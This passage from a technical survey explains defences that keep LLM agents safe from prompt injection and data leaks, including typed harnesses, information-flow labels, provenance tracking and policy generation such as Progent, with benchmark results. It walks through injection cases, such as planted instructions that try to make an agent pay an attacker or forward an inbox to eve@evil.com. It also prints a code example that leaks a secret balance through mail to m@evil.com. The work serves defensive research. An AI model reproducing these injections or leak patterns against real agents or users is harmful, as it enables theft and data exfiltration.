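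The agent can still work with secrets. It can pass a wrapped document to a separate, trusted model and get back a wrapped summary. If it prints the summary, the user's screen shows the text, but the agent's own model receives only "Classified(****)". The agent lacks the further capability needed to release the text, so a company that marked its payroll file as classified could let an agent post opening hours without letting it post salaries.

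Types also limit how long a permission lasts. TACIT grants access to a directory for one block of code, and the compiler rejects a block whose result captures that access, so an agent cannot save a file handle and use it after the block ends. Scala has features that would let code escape this tracking, such as reflection, which finds and runs code by name. TACIT compiles the agent's programs in a "safe mode" that forbids those features.

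### How TACIT performed

Odersky and colleagues built a small software project with a directory of secrets. They combined 12 user tasks with 10 injections and added 11 requests in which the user asked for secrets directly or under a false pretext. The table shows how often the agent's output contained no secrets.

| Model and test | With Classified | Without Classified |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, 120 injection trials | 100% | 100% |
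| Claude Sonnet 4.6, 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| MiniMax M2.5, 120 injection trials | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |

The injections rarely worked even without the wrapper, so most of the improvement came from blocking hostile users. The design also nearly guarantees the perfect scores, since the agent's model never receives the wrapped text. The task completion rates are more informative. With the wrapper, the agents still completed 99.2% and 90.0% of the user tasks, compared with 83.3% and 88.3% without it.

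On AgentDojo, only one attack across two models counted as a success. The agent had booked the right hotel but quoted a review recommending the attacker's hotel. TACIT's utility relative to CaMeL's varied widely, though Odersky and colleagues describe the two as comparable. With OpenAI's o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of the workspace tasks and CaMeL 81.4%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64.3% of the travel tasks and CaMeL 1.4%.

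### One language for the agent and its harness

TACIT checks the programs that an agent submits, but the harness around the agent can be written in any language. In ELBA, a Haskell system by Zhou and colleagues, the agent's programs and the harness are in the same typed language. A developer's program calls a function named `agent` as follows.

1. The developer supplies a prompt, a list of functions the agent may use, and the type of result the program needs.
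2. The model writes a Haskell program of that type.
3. The compiler checks it. If the check fails, the model receives the error and tries again.
4. The program runs. It can itself call `agent`, passing on what it has learned, so the system can look at one result before it chooses the next step. The inner call has to obey the same policy or a stricter one.

One policy requires every bibliography entry to come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that fetches an entry returns it with the type Trusted, which no other code can create, and the function that writes to the bibliography accepts only that type. In 100 tasks, ELBA wrote 925 citations and none had a false author, year or DOI. An ordinary agent with a web search tool got 19 of 1,002 wrong.

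Including the harness matters because a leak can occur outside the code that a monitor watches. *The LLMbda Calculus* describes such a leak in CaMeL, whose interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop that retries failed attempts. Whether an attempt fails can depend on a secret, which reveals one bit, and repeated attempts can reveal the whole secret. ELBA retries only after a type error, which occurs before the new program has called any tool.

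Zhou and colleagues prove that any property the language's types guarantee for ordinary programs also holds for programs that call agents. The proof limits how deeply agent calls can nest, then replaces each call with an ordinary function that queries the model, type-checks the answer and runs it. Calls inside that answer have a smaller depth limit, so the replacement eventually ends. The result is an ordinary program that makes the same tool calls, so the language's existing guarantee applies to it. The proof treats the model as an arbitrary source of programs, so it holds even if an attacker controls the model's entire output. The proof does not show that the developer chose the right policy.

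### Whether code and data still need separating

Willison's dual-LLM pattern and CaMeL keep untrusted text away from the model that plans, so the text cannot add a step to the plan. ELBA instead lets a model read untrusted text and then write the next program. Zhou and colleagues argue that strict separation of code and data is an unnecessary workaround when a typed language limits what that next program can do.

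They tested this on AgentDojo's Slack tasks with LIO, an existing Haskell library that labels data by its source. When a computation reads untrusted data, LIO lowers that computation's privileges, and any later action that needs higher privileges fails. To simulate an injection that always works, whenever a sub-agent received the attacker's text, they made that text its entire prompt. They ran each of the 105 attack cases seven times, for 735 runs per model.

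| Model | Attacks resisted, no policy | Attacks resisted, with policy | Tasks completed, no policy | Tasks completed, with policy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 425 | 735 | 523 | 351 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 460 | 735 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT 5.4 | 621 | 735 | 558 | 338 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 540 | 735 | 494 | 294 |

The policies stopped every attack, although the hijacked sub-agents followed the attacker's instructions. Without attacks and with policies on, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of the 21 tasks, depending on the model, while CaMeL completed 4 to 6. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL, mainly because it queries the model again after reading data.

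These results support dropping the separation of code from data as a fixed architecture, but ELBA still separates them in places. For example, an agent can ask a sub-agent to write a message, receive it sealed, and pass it to the sending tool without reading it. Willison's privileged model also passes on VAR2 without reading it. ELBA's advantage is that a program can choose when to isolate a sub-agent, and the sub-agent can still use any tool that its label permits. *The LLMbda Calculus* likewise treats isolation as a policy that a program can express.

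An agent loses privileges when it directly reads untrusted text, which helps explain why the policies reduced the number of completed tasks by 33% to 44%. The debugging agent discussed earlier would presumably have the same problem. It could read a failure log and plan a repair, but if an attacker could have written part of the log, a strict policy would stop the agent from changing trusted code.

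Separation also remains useful where a policy grants more than the task needs. For example, ELBA's file policy confines a program to certain directories but does not label data, so a hijacked sub-agent could overwrite any file in them. A plan fixed in advance would include only the writes that the request called for. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) reports a few failures that fit this explanation. Its Scala system, a successor to TACIT, also lets generated programs call the model again. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, 7 of 949 AgentDojo attacks succeeded against this system and none against CaMeL. With o4-mini-high, one attack succeeded against each. The paper notes that the system's types cannot stop an attacker from misusing a capability that the task legitimately grants.

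### Checking before and during a run

Static checking, which means checking a program before it runs, prevents a rejected program from leaving work half done. In an example from LACUNA, a program subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the caller needs a number. The compiler rejects both lines, so the balance stays at 100. Python would have subtracted the 50 before reaching the error.

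A static check also covers lines that a particular run skips. *The LLMbda Calculus* adapts a classic example to CaMeL, roughly as follows, with the account balance as the secret:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the third line changes `tmp`, and CaMeL labels it secret. The program then skips the assignment in the fourth line, so CaMeL never updates the label on `rich`. `rich` stays True and public, and the e-mail goes out. If the balance is lower, no e-mail goes out. The attacker therefore learns which side of the threshold the balance is on. A static checker for data flows would examine the fourth line even when the program skips it, and would mark `rich` as dependent on the balance.

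Run-time checks can be sound too. *The LLMbda Calculus* presents a language that tracks labels while a program runs, and a machine-checked proof that secrets cannot influence public results, except through whether the program finishes. An agent built in the language resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks on AgentDojo's banking tasks.

A compiler cannot check facts that are available only while the program runs, such as where a file path leads when the program computes it from a web page. TACIT therefore checks at run time that each path stays inside the permitted directory, and ELBA also follows symbolic links, which are files that redirect to other locations. ELBA's types ensure that a program can act only through LIO, but LIO compares the labels as the program runs. A program can therefore compile and still stop partway because of its policy.

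### Unfamiliar languages and harmless programs

Models are trained on much less Scala than Python, and the evidence on how much this matters is mixed. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of real software bugs, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it.

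On τ²-bench, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% of the tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. Zhao and colleagues call these results "on par", despite the gap of 14 percentage points. The compiler rejected 22.4% of that model's programs for the retail tasks, whereas at most 7.9% of programs under TACIT needed a retry. With the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, it rejected 3.2% of programs for the retail tasks and 89% for the telecom tasks. Stronger models had little trouble with ELBA's Haskell, and only 7 of 2,688 runs used up their retries. Rejected programs never run, so poor code slows the agent and reduces the number of tasks it completes but does not weaken the protection.

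The compiler also rejects some harmless programs. One agent using TACIT wrote a function to print the first five lines of a file, which it had permission to do. The compiler rejected the program because the agent had left out the symbol that marks the file as a tracked capability. A model can usually fix such mistakes using the error message. In ELBA, retries took only 3.4% of the running time, so the strict types were a much smaller burden than the strict policies.

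### Tools and wrappers that the compiler cannot check

A compiler's guarantees don't cover other programs that the typed program starts. If an agent's Scala code runs git or a Python script, TACIT can only check the command against a list, and a sandbox has to contain whatever the command does. Coding agents run such commands constantly, so TACIT leaves them with the same gap as CapScope does with pytest.

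Developers also have to write typed wrappers for their tools. TACIT's reusable library is about 1,000 lines long, and each customer-service domain needed a few hundred more. An existing agent such as Claude Code can connect to TACIT without changes, but the developer has to remove its other tools, since a command sent directly to the shell would bypass the compiler. ELBA requires the whole harness to be written in Haskell, while most agent frameworks use Python.

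The compiler is part of what users have to trust. Scala's capability tracking is still experimental, but it is fast enough for everyday use. *What's in the Box* (2025) reports that it took less than 15% of the compile time for Scala's standard library. The underlying type system has machine-checked proofs, but Odersky and colleagues say a further argument is needed to show that safe mode delivers what it promises.

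The wrappers need just as much trust, because the compiler relies on the types their developers give them. A developer can mark a library module as safe, and the compiler then skips its usual restrictions on it. TACIT's function for consulting the trusted model counts as pure, although it sends text to another service, and the compiler cannot check whether that service keeps a record. In the AgentDojo tests, the banking wrapper's payment function lists no capability, so a program can apparently call it from inside `map`. This lets an agent pay a bill that its model cannot read, but the program would also pass a false account number from the bill to the payment function.

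## Tracking where data came from and where it may go

TACIT's payment function would accept a false account number from a bill because the program keeps no record of who supplied the number. Information-flow control adds that record. Software attaches a label to each piece of data, computes labels for whatever a program derives from it, and checks the labels before the data reaches a tool. CaMeL's tags and the LIO library in ELBA work this way. The method dates from the 1970s and suits ordinary programs well, but it is harder to apply to agents because nobody can tell exactly which parts of the input a language model used.

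### Integrity, confidentiality and the order of labels

An integrity label records how far the system trusts the sources of a piece of data. The simplest scheme has two values, trusted (T) and untrusted (U). A confidentiality label records who may see the data, and the simplest scheme again has two values, public (L, for low) and secret (H, for high). The two labels are independent. A web page is usually untrusted and public, while a company's payroll file is trusted and secret.

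Dorothy Denning's 1976 paper *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* arranged such labels in an order, where *a* ⊑ *b* means that data labelled *a* may flow to a place labelled *b*. Public data may enter a secret file, so L ⊑ H, and trusted data may go wherever the system accepts untrusted data, so T ⊑ U. The reverse flows are forbidden. In a lattice, any two labels also have a least upper bound, or join, written *a* ⊔ *b*, which is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both. Anything computed from two inputs receives the join of their labels, so T ⊔ U = U and L ⊔ H = H.

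Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) explain in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* that labels can also be sets of people. If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dave may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a text that draws on both. For confidentiality, the join is therefore the intersection of the two sets of readers. For integrity, it is the union of the two sets of possible writers, because anyone who could have influenced either document could have influenced the combined text.

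In 1977 Kenneth Biba stated two rules for integrity. A process may not read data of lower integrity than its own, and may not write to data of higher integrity. Applied strictly, the first rule would bar an agent that can make payments from opening a web page. Biba also described a looser version, in which a process may read anything but drops to the level of the least trusted data it has read. An agent with one label for its whole conversation follows this looser version.

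### One summary and two addresses

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise a web page and mail the summary to anna@example.com. The policy for sending mail requires the choice of tool and the recipient to be trusted, but allows an untrusted body.

1. The harness labels the user's request, including Anna's address, as trusted and public.
2. It fetches the page, labels it untrusted and public, and keeps it away from the model that plans.
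3. A separate model summarises the page. The summary depends on a trusted instruction and an untrusted page, so its integrity label is T ⊔ U = U.
4. The planning model proposes to send the summary to Anna. The tool and the recipient are trusted, so the harness sends the message.

If the user then asks the agent to mail the summary to the contact address on the page, the recipient's label is U, so the harness blocks the call even if the address is genuine. CaMeL would do the same with Bob's address.

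Confidentiality labels can block the first message too. If the summary also draws on a memo that only Ben and Carol may read, Anna is not permitted to read the summary, so the harness does not send it to her.

### FIDES: hiding only what would change the label

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built these rules into a planner called FIDES. They began with an ordinary agent loop in which the conversation's label is the join of all its messages' labels. One untrusted e-mail makes the whole conversation untrusted, and the policy then blocks every consequential call for the rest of the session. FIDES avoids this by hiding data from the planning model.

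1. Each tool returns its result with a label on every field.
2. FIDES compares each label with that of the conversation. If a field would make the conversation's label more restrictive, FIDES stores the field in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. Other fields stay visible, so the model might see an e-mail's date but not its subject.
3. The model can pass a variable to a tool, or ask a quarantined model a question about it. The answer goes into a new variable.
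4. The model can also open a variable with a tool called inspect. The conversation then takes on the variable's label.
5. Before each tool call, a policy engine checks the labels of the call and its arguments. One policy allows consequential calls only if they are trusted. Another allows data to leave only if every recipient may read it.

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) treats FIDES and CaMeL as two implementations of Willison's dual-LLM pattern. Whereas CaMeL writes a whole program at the start, FIDES chooses each step after the previous one, so it can change its plan in response to anything it is allowed to see.

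When the plan has to depend on hidden text, FIDES can restrict the type of answer the quarantined model gives about that text, much as Jacob and colleagues do. Suppose the user asks the agent to read three e-mails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting. The quarantined model answers yes or no, and the planning model reads only that answer. If the answer is yes, the planning model has the quarantined model extract the details into a variable, which it passes to the calendar. FIDES records each answer's type in the answer's label, so a policy can accept an untrusted yes or no but refuse an untrusted sentence.

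The tests used AgentDojo, GPT-4o and one of the benchmark's stock attacks. The table gives the share of tasks completed when there was no attack, then the number of successful attacks after Costa and colleagues removed cases that the benchmark had misjudged.

| Planner | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no policy checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% | 152 |
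| Ordinary, with checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% | 0 |
| FIDES, no checks | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% | 21 |
| FIDES, with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% | 0 |

The policy checks alone stopped every attack, even in the ordinary planner. Hiding data let the agent complete some of the tasks that the checks had blocked. FIDES with checks completed an average of 50% of tasks across the four environments, compared with 42% for the ordinary planner with checks and 84% for the ordinary planner without them. Its lead over the checked ordinary planner grew from 8 to 16 percentage points with OpenAI's o1, which used the variables more reliably. Most of the remaining failures were intended. For example, many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the policy forbids. The tested version of FIDES did not restrict the form of the quarantined model's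 answers, so these results do not show how well the yes-or-no mechanism works.

### Why labels spread

A join can only keep a label the same or make it more restrictive, so a long session tends towards a single label, untrusted and secret. Security researchers call this label creep. It also happens in ordinary programs, but software can slow it down there by tracking individual values. In the line `total = price + tax`, for example, `total` depends only on `price` and `tax`.

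Databases allow the same precision, because their operations have exact definitions. *Please Don't Kill My Vibe* (2025) proposes to enforce data-flow policies inside the database, so that they apply regardless of what the agent's developer has done. *Environment Steering* (2026) describes the method as giving each input row an identifier and each output row an expression that shows its origins. The expression *b*₁ × *p*₂ means that rows *b*₁ and *p*₂ jointly produced the output, and a plus sign marks alternative derivations. A policy can then require, for example, that any private rows behind an answer belong to the user who asked. The method covers single queries, so it can't trace data once a model rewrites the answer or the agent takes several steps.

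Every token in a language model's context can affect every token it writes, through billions of learned weights, so there is no equivalent of the line that computes `total`. If an agent proposes an address that appears both in the user's contacts and on a web page, nobody can tell from the model's internal state which one it used. The only safe assumption is that the output depends on the whole context. FIDES therefore controls what enters the context instead of trying to trace influences inside the model.

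### RTBAS: estimating which data mattered

*RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, Carnegie Mellon University, 2025) takes a different approach to label creep, using a model to judge which parts of the conversation matter for the next step.

1. The harness divides the conversation into labelled regions.
2. A screener selects the regions that the next step depends on. In one version, the screener is a second language model. In the other, a small open model reads the conversation, and a trained classifier uses its attention scores to make the selection.
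3. The harness joins the labels of the selected regions.
4. It removes every region whose label is more restrictive than the result.
5. The agent's model proposes a tool call from what remains.
6. If the tool's policy does not accept the joined label, the system asks the user to confirm the call.

Because of the fourth step, a screener's mistake does not let an attack through. If the screener overlooks a poisoned web page and selects only trusted regions, the harness removes the page, so it cannot influence the call. If the screener selects the page, the call counts as untrusted. The classifier was right only 81% of the time on held-out data, but its errors led to unfinished tasks and extra confirmations rather than security failures. An attacker who fooled the screener could still influence which of the few possible labels it produced, and so cause needless questions or hide information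 the task requires.

Zhong and colleagues ran the 629 AgentDojo cases and refused every call that would have needed confirmation. No attack that violated their policy succeeded. Without an attack, the share of tasks completed fell by 10 percentage points with the second model as screener and by 7.4 with the classifier. Completion fell most on the Slack tasks, to 22% and 33% respectively, because many of them require the agent to act on website content. In the banking tasks, using a second model roughly doubled the cost, from 1.5 to 3.2 cents per task, and the time, from 4.4 to 9.7 seconds.

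### Leaks through decisions and errors

Labels on values miss some of what data can reveal. Suppose an agent reads a secret memo and books a large room if a merger is going ahead or a small one if it is not. The booking contains no text from the memo, yet anyone who can see the calendar learns the decision. Security researchers call this an implicit flow, because the information passes through the agent's choice of room. The CaMeL program that revealed an account balance through a skipped assignment had the same flaw.

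FIDES guarantees only a property called explicit secrecy. Take the tool calls that a particular run makes, and let *g* be the function by which those calls turn the initial data into the final data. Write *d*₁ =_L *d*₂ if two sets of data agree on every public item. Explicit secrecy requires that

if *d*₁ =_L *d*₂, then *g*(*d*₁) =_L *g*(*d*₂).

Although changing a secret cannot change what these particular calls write to public places, it can change which calls the agent makes, and therefore which *g* applies. Noninterference, a stronger property, rules out both effects. Costa and colleagues rejected it as too restrictive because it would in effect ban any tool that may write public data once the agent has used a tool that may read secrets. Neither the labels nor the proof covers indirect signals such as the timing of calls.

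Errors can carry information in the same way. When a policy refuses a call, FIDES tells the planning model, which may try something else. If the refusal depended on secret data, an outsider who notices a missing or different message can learn something about that data.

Implicit flows also weaken integrity. In the meeting example, whoever wrote the e-mail decides whether the agent creates an event. One yes-or-no answer gives an attacker little control, but twenty can select one of about a million options. The label does not record how many answers the agent has used, because the join of two yes-or-no labels is another yes-or-no label. A policy that limits an attacker's total influence would have to count the answers separately.

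### PACE: tracking paths and checking authority

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) combines provenance with the kind of permission check that CapScope and AgentCap use. Its software maintains a graph of each session, with nodes for data, operations and resources and arrows for the flows between them. When the model proposes a call, the software looks up each argument among the values it has recorded. If it finds a match, it links the argument to that value's history. The software then runs two checks on the call.

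- **The path check** looks for routes through the graph from untrusted or protected data to an unsafe effect, and for the cheapest way to cut them. It cannot undo earlier calls, so the cut has to fall on the proposed one. In practice this usually means blocking it.
- **The effect check** asks whether the user's own request authorises what the call would do, including its target, its arguments and how often it may run.

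Li and colleagues formally analyse a design in which a call must pass both checks. In the version they tested, the effect check can restore a call that the path check has blocked, so the proof that untrusted data cannot reach an unsafe effect does not cover that version. They examined the parts separately on 1,167 cases with a local model, Qwen-3.8-27B. The table shows the results for AgentDojo and AgentDyn, another benchmark of agents under attack.

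| Checks in use | AgentDojo, attack success | AgentDojo, tasks completed | AgentDyn, attack success | AgentDyn, tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% |
| Path check only | 0% | 13.6% | 0% | 0% |
| Effect check only | 0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% |
| Full system, as tested | 0% | 67.2% | 0% | 33.3% |

The path check on its own made the agent nearly useless. In the AgentDyn runs, it proposed a cut for 5,842 of 6,647 calls, which indicates how far untrusted influence spreads through a session. The agent could complete tasks again because the effect check overruled the path check. Li and colleagues attribute most of the security to the effect check and acknowledge that the full combination showed no security benefit of its own in this experiment.

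The full system did well in the larger tests on eight benchmarks with three models. On AgentDojo, the worst group of attacks succeeded in 0% to 8.1% of cases, compared with 48% to 100% for undefended agents, and the defended agents completed almost as many tasks as the undefended ones. The weakest result was on InjecAgent, where 30.8% of attacks succeeded against a GPT model. In a small adaptive test, an automated search beat the undefended agent in 21 of 30 cases and PACE in none. With so few cases, the true success rate against PACE could be as high as 11%.

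The graph has gaps wherever a model rewrites text. PACE can detect a protected value in certain standard encodings, but not after a model has paraphrased, translated or split it.

### Separate sources for each field

In *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*, Santos-Grueiro (2026) argues that a system should track what influenced a tool call, not just where the characters in it came from. The name of a tool always comes from a trusted list, but untrusted text may have led the model to choose that tool. The paper's system, CXI, therefore keeps a set of influences for each protected field of a call and another for the decision to make, retry or schedule the call.

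In CXI, untrusted text can fill a protected field only through a "typed release". Suppose an agent reads the log of a failed test, which an attacker may have written in part. Trusted code can take a file path from the log, check it against the repository, and release it for the file-path field alone. The same path cannot fill the command field, and the word "approved" in the log cannot fill the approval field. The agent may quote the log in a comment, but if another agent reads the comment, CXI treats the text as untrusted again.

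The system still has to know what influenced each field. In its strictest form, CXI has the model write each protected field in a separate run, from a prompt that contains only trusted material and values released for that field, so the log cannot influence the run because it is never included. This requires control over the software that runs the model. When a provider hosts the model, the developer can control and record the prompts but cannot inspect the provider's stored internal state. The faster versions that Santos-Grueiro tested on open models also give weaker evidence than the strict form, because they exclude only the sources of influence the software has declared.

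A bug fix has to depend on untrusted text such as the bug report, so no rule based only on where data came from can approve it. CXI computes exactly how the patch would change the repository, and trusted code accepts or rejects that change, for instance rejecting patches that disable automated tests or add installation scripts. The approval lapses if the patch or the repository later changes at all. This partly protects the debugging agent, whose repairs depend on a log that an attacker can influence, but it cannot show that the patch fixes the bug or does no subtler damage.

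In 400 coding episodes, the agent completed 231 tasks safely, and no unauthorised action ran. Of the other 169 episodes, 73 had output that the software could not parse, 61 had no authorised change, and 35 had an authorised change that failed to complete the task. "Unauthorised" here means contrary to the policy, which takes care to write correctly. An audit of the rules for 24 kinds of action, with 149 fields in total, initially found 18 problems, half of them severe. Some rules treated text that could change a system's behaviour as harmless data.

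### Who assigns the first label

Joins and checks rely on accurate initial labels, which software usually has to guess. FIDES infers who may read an e-mail from its sender and recipients, although someone may have shared it more widely. For its AgentDojo tests, Costa and colleagues labelled a field untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. This gives a clear baseline, but a company cannot label its own data this way because it does not know which fields future attacks will use.

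One banking task shows a limit of such labels. The user asks the agent to change the password if it finds a suspicious transaction. FIDES hid the untrusted transaction descriptions from the model but showed it the amounts and dates, which were labelled trusted. The model classified one large amount as suspicious and changed the password, which the policy allowed. This was not an attack, but anyone who can send the user money also chooses the amount, and could use it to influence the agent's decision.

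Designs differ on what to do when a label is missing. RTBAS treats an unlabelled region as trusted and public, so if a developer forgets to label a new tool's output, an attacker can use that tool freely. CXI rejects any call in which a protected field has unknown provenance, so the same oversight stops the agent from working. CXI's failure is safer, and the developer will probably notice it sooner.

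Data can also lose its label in storage. Zhong and colleagues describe a tool that accepts private text in a message and another that returns sent messages as public data. An agent could send itself a secret and read it back without its private label. Every tool that stores data therefore has to store its labels too.

A trusted party can deliberately raise a label, which is called endorsement. Costa and colleagues suggest that a system might upgrade a document from untrusted to trusted after an injection classifier has passed it, but they warn that relying on such detectors can weaken the guarantee. Nasr and colleagues support this warning with adaptive attacks that easily got past such classifiers.

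Text that a user pastes into the chat is the hardest case. By default, FIDES labels the user's messages as trusted, so the instructions and payment details in a pasted e-mail count as trusted in every later check. Zhong and colleagues found a similar problem in AgentDojo, where text written by the user contained a possible injection that RTBAS did not track. An interface could label pasted passages as untrusted, but that would block a payment to an account number the user pasted on purpose. Zheng and colleagues accept this drawback in IntentCap for destinations and approvals.

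### When the harness compresses the conversation

Labels can also disappear during a session. When a conversation nears the limit of the model's context window, the harness has a model summarise the earlier part and continues from the summary. In *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026) recorded 1,108 automatic summaries in two coding agents, Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex. In every case, the harness inserted the summary as a user message, which gave text from tools, web pages and attackers the user's authority.

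This matters for systems such as Progent, which has a model write a policy from the user's request and enforces it in code. In one example, a user asks a banking agent about spending in March. A transaction description contains an instruction to pay the attacker, and Progent blocks the payment because the question doesn't require one. The summary later lists the blocked payment as unfinished work. Progent derives its next policy from the summary, and that policy permits one transfer, to the attacker's account.

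When the summary was in the user's position, 17 of 30 new policies allowed the attacker's transfer. When Fei and colleagues supplied the same summaries as tool results, none of 28 policies did. In complete runs after compression, attacks succeeded against Progent in 31 of 100 cases, compared with 33 for an undefended agent. Progent's own integrations avoid the problem by writing one policy per session. Fei and colleagues instead used a new policy for each request, because an agent with a frozen policy completed only 7 of 60 follow-up tasks, compared with 41 of 60 when the policy was renewed.

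Better summaries help only partly. The policy named the attacker's account in 349 of 536 cases where the summary kept the account number without comment, but in only 7 of 230 where the summary used a word such as "suspicious" or "untrusted". Leading models often flag injected commands, but they rarely flag a false account number that looks like ordinary data. In one test, the user had already named the payee for the rent, and a planted notice gave a different account. Policies based on the summary allowed payment to the planted account in 91% of cases with one policy-writing model and 59% with another, while policies based on the user's own words never allowed it.

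Fei and colleagues prove that this limit applies to any system that sees only text. Let *p*_L be the probability that the system accepts a value from a legitimate record, and *p*_A the probability that it accepts one from an attacker's record. Then

*p*_L − *p*_A ≤ TV,

where TV is again the total variation distance, here between what the system reads when the record is genuine and what it reads when the record is forged. If the attacker imitates a genuine record perfectly, TV is 0, and the system must accept both equally often.

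Their solution gives the agent and the policy writer different inputs. The harness attaches a cryptographic tag to each user message when it arrives. When the context is compressed, the harness copies the tagged messages word for word into an ordered list. The agent reads the summary, while the policy writer receives only the list. Before the policy writer receives it, software checks the tags, the order and the number of messages. It checks the number because a missing message might be a cancellation. If any check fails, the policy permits nothing. In 40 attacked episodes with this gate in place, no attacker's action succeeded.

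The tags record which channel a message came through, so text that the user pasted counts as the user's own. They also do not help when the user lets a document supply a value, as in a request to pay whatever account an invoice lists. Fei and colleagues show that unless a system can authenticate who issued an invoice, it can refuse forged invoices more often than genuine ones only to the extent that their text differs.

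## Who writes the policy, and who decides unclear cases

Fei and colleagues' gate shows the policy writer only the user's messages. But the policy writer is still a language model, and the monitor enforces whatever rules that model produces. An attacker can do harm without breaking a rule that permits too much, and the agent can't finish its work if a rule permits too little.

### A rule and its default

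Xiang and colleagues print a small rule in Cedar, an authorisation language from Amazon Web Services:

```
permit(
  principal == User::"alice",
  action == Action::"view",
  resource == Document::"doc1"
);
```

This rule permits one user, Alice, to view one document, doc1. If the policy contains no other rules, Alice cannot edit doc1 and Bob cannot view it, because Cedar refuses any request that no rule permits (default denial). Cedar also has "forbid" rules, which override "permit" rules.

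The policy's default determines what happens when its author forgets a case. If the system denies whatever no rule allows, the agent fails at something it should be able to do, and the user will probably complain. If the system allows whatever no rule forbids, as Madatha's list of dangerous shell commands does, a forgotten case stays open until someone exploits it. But denying by default doesn't help when a rule permits too much.

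### A payment rule that fails in both directions

Xiang and colleagues point out that CaMeL's payment rule blocks a request to pay a bill from xyz@abc.com but allows an inflated payment to Joe for his bouquet. Suppose the bill is for $120 and the bouquet cost $40, but someone has planted a $400 price on the web page where the agent looks it up. The table compares CaMeL's condition on the recipient with three possible repairs.

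| Rule for payments | Genuine bill, $120 | Bouquet, real price of $40 | Bouquet, planted price of $400 |
|---|---|---|---|
| The recipient comes from the user | Blocked | Allowed | Allowed |
| The recipient and the amount come from the user | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |
| The recipient comes from the user or from a bill the user mentioned | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| The same, with a limit of $150 | Allowed | Allowed | Blocked |

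The last rule gives the right answer in all three cases, but only because the attacker asked for too much. A planted price of $149 would pass, and so would a forged bill for the same amount. Setting a tighter limit for the bouquet would require knowing roughly what it cost, which is what the agent was trying to find out.

Xiang and colleagues conclude that one rule for all payments will be too strict for some tasks and too lenient for others. Even a policy written for a single task may be incomplete when the task begins. In one AgentDojo task, the user asks the agent to invite a new colleague to Slack, using details in a message from Bob. The strictest workable policy would allow only an invitation to that person and access to the channels Bob lists, but nobody can write it until the agent has read Bob's message.

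### Progent: a policy that changes during the task

*Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025) has a model write a policy for each task and revise it as the agent works. Each rule allows or forbids calls to one tool when the arguments meet certain conditions, such as a maximum amount or a recipient on a list. A rule also specifies whether a blocked call stops the agent, asks the user, or returns an error message. Before each tool call, ordinary code applies the "forbid" rules first, then the "allow" rules, and blocks the call if no rule matches.

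In the paper's main example, a user asks an agent to carry out the actions in an e-mail titled "TODOs for the week". The first policy allows only a search for that e-mail.

| What the agent learns | Change to the policy | How Progent treats it |
|---|---|---|
| The list asks for a summary of recent e-mails, posted to the user's Slack | Allow reading mail, looking up the user's Slack name and posting to Slack | Expansion, which needs approval |
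| The user's Slack name is alice | Allow Slack posts only to alice | Narrowing, which takes effect automatically |
| One of the recent e-mails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to eve@evil.com | None or, if the injection fools the policy model, allow sending mail | An added permission would be an expansion and need approval |

If the agent follows the injection and tries to send the inbox to Eve, the code blocks the call because no rule allows it. The agent receives an error message and then posts the summary.

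The policy model reads untrusted text, so Progent doesn't rely on it to classify its own changes. Write *A*(*P*) for the set of tool calls that a policy *P* allows. A new policy *P*′ is a narrowing if

*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*),

and otherwise it is an expansion. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether a logical formula can be true, makes the comparison. For each tool, it looks for arguments that *P*′ would accept and *P* would refuse. If there are none, the change takes effect. The set of allowed calls can therefore only shrink between approvals, a property that Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement.

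They also split each update into two model calls. The first decides whether a tool call might require a new policy, without seeing the tool's result. The second reads the result and drafts the change.

Shi and colleagues tested several ways of handling expansions on AgentDojo, using GPT-4o both as the agent and to write the policies.

| Setting | Attack success |
|---|---|
| No defence | 39.9% |
| First policy only, never updated | 2.5% |
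| Every expansion approved automatically | 1.0% |
| Every expansion refused automatically | Slightly lower than with automatic approval |
| A person reviews the first policy and every expansion | 0% |

The paper's main result, a fall from 39.9% to 1.0%, comes from the setting with automatic approval, which Shi and colleagues chose to imitate a careless user. In that setting, every update took effect whatever the solver found, so the solver contributed nothing to the result. The fall occurred because GPT-4o usually wrote good policies and the code enforced them. Most of the improvement came from the first policy, which the model wrote before reading any untrusted text.

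The agent completed about as many tasks with the defence as without it. On a second benchmark, Agent Security Bench, the attack success rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the remaining attacks used tools with names and descriptions very similar to those of legitimate tools, and hand-written rules stopped them all. Shi and colleagues also planted instructions for the policy model to allow every tool, which raised the attack success rate only slightly, even with automatic approval. Narisetty and colleagues later got a similar result with a small open model.

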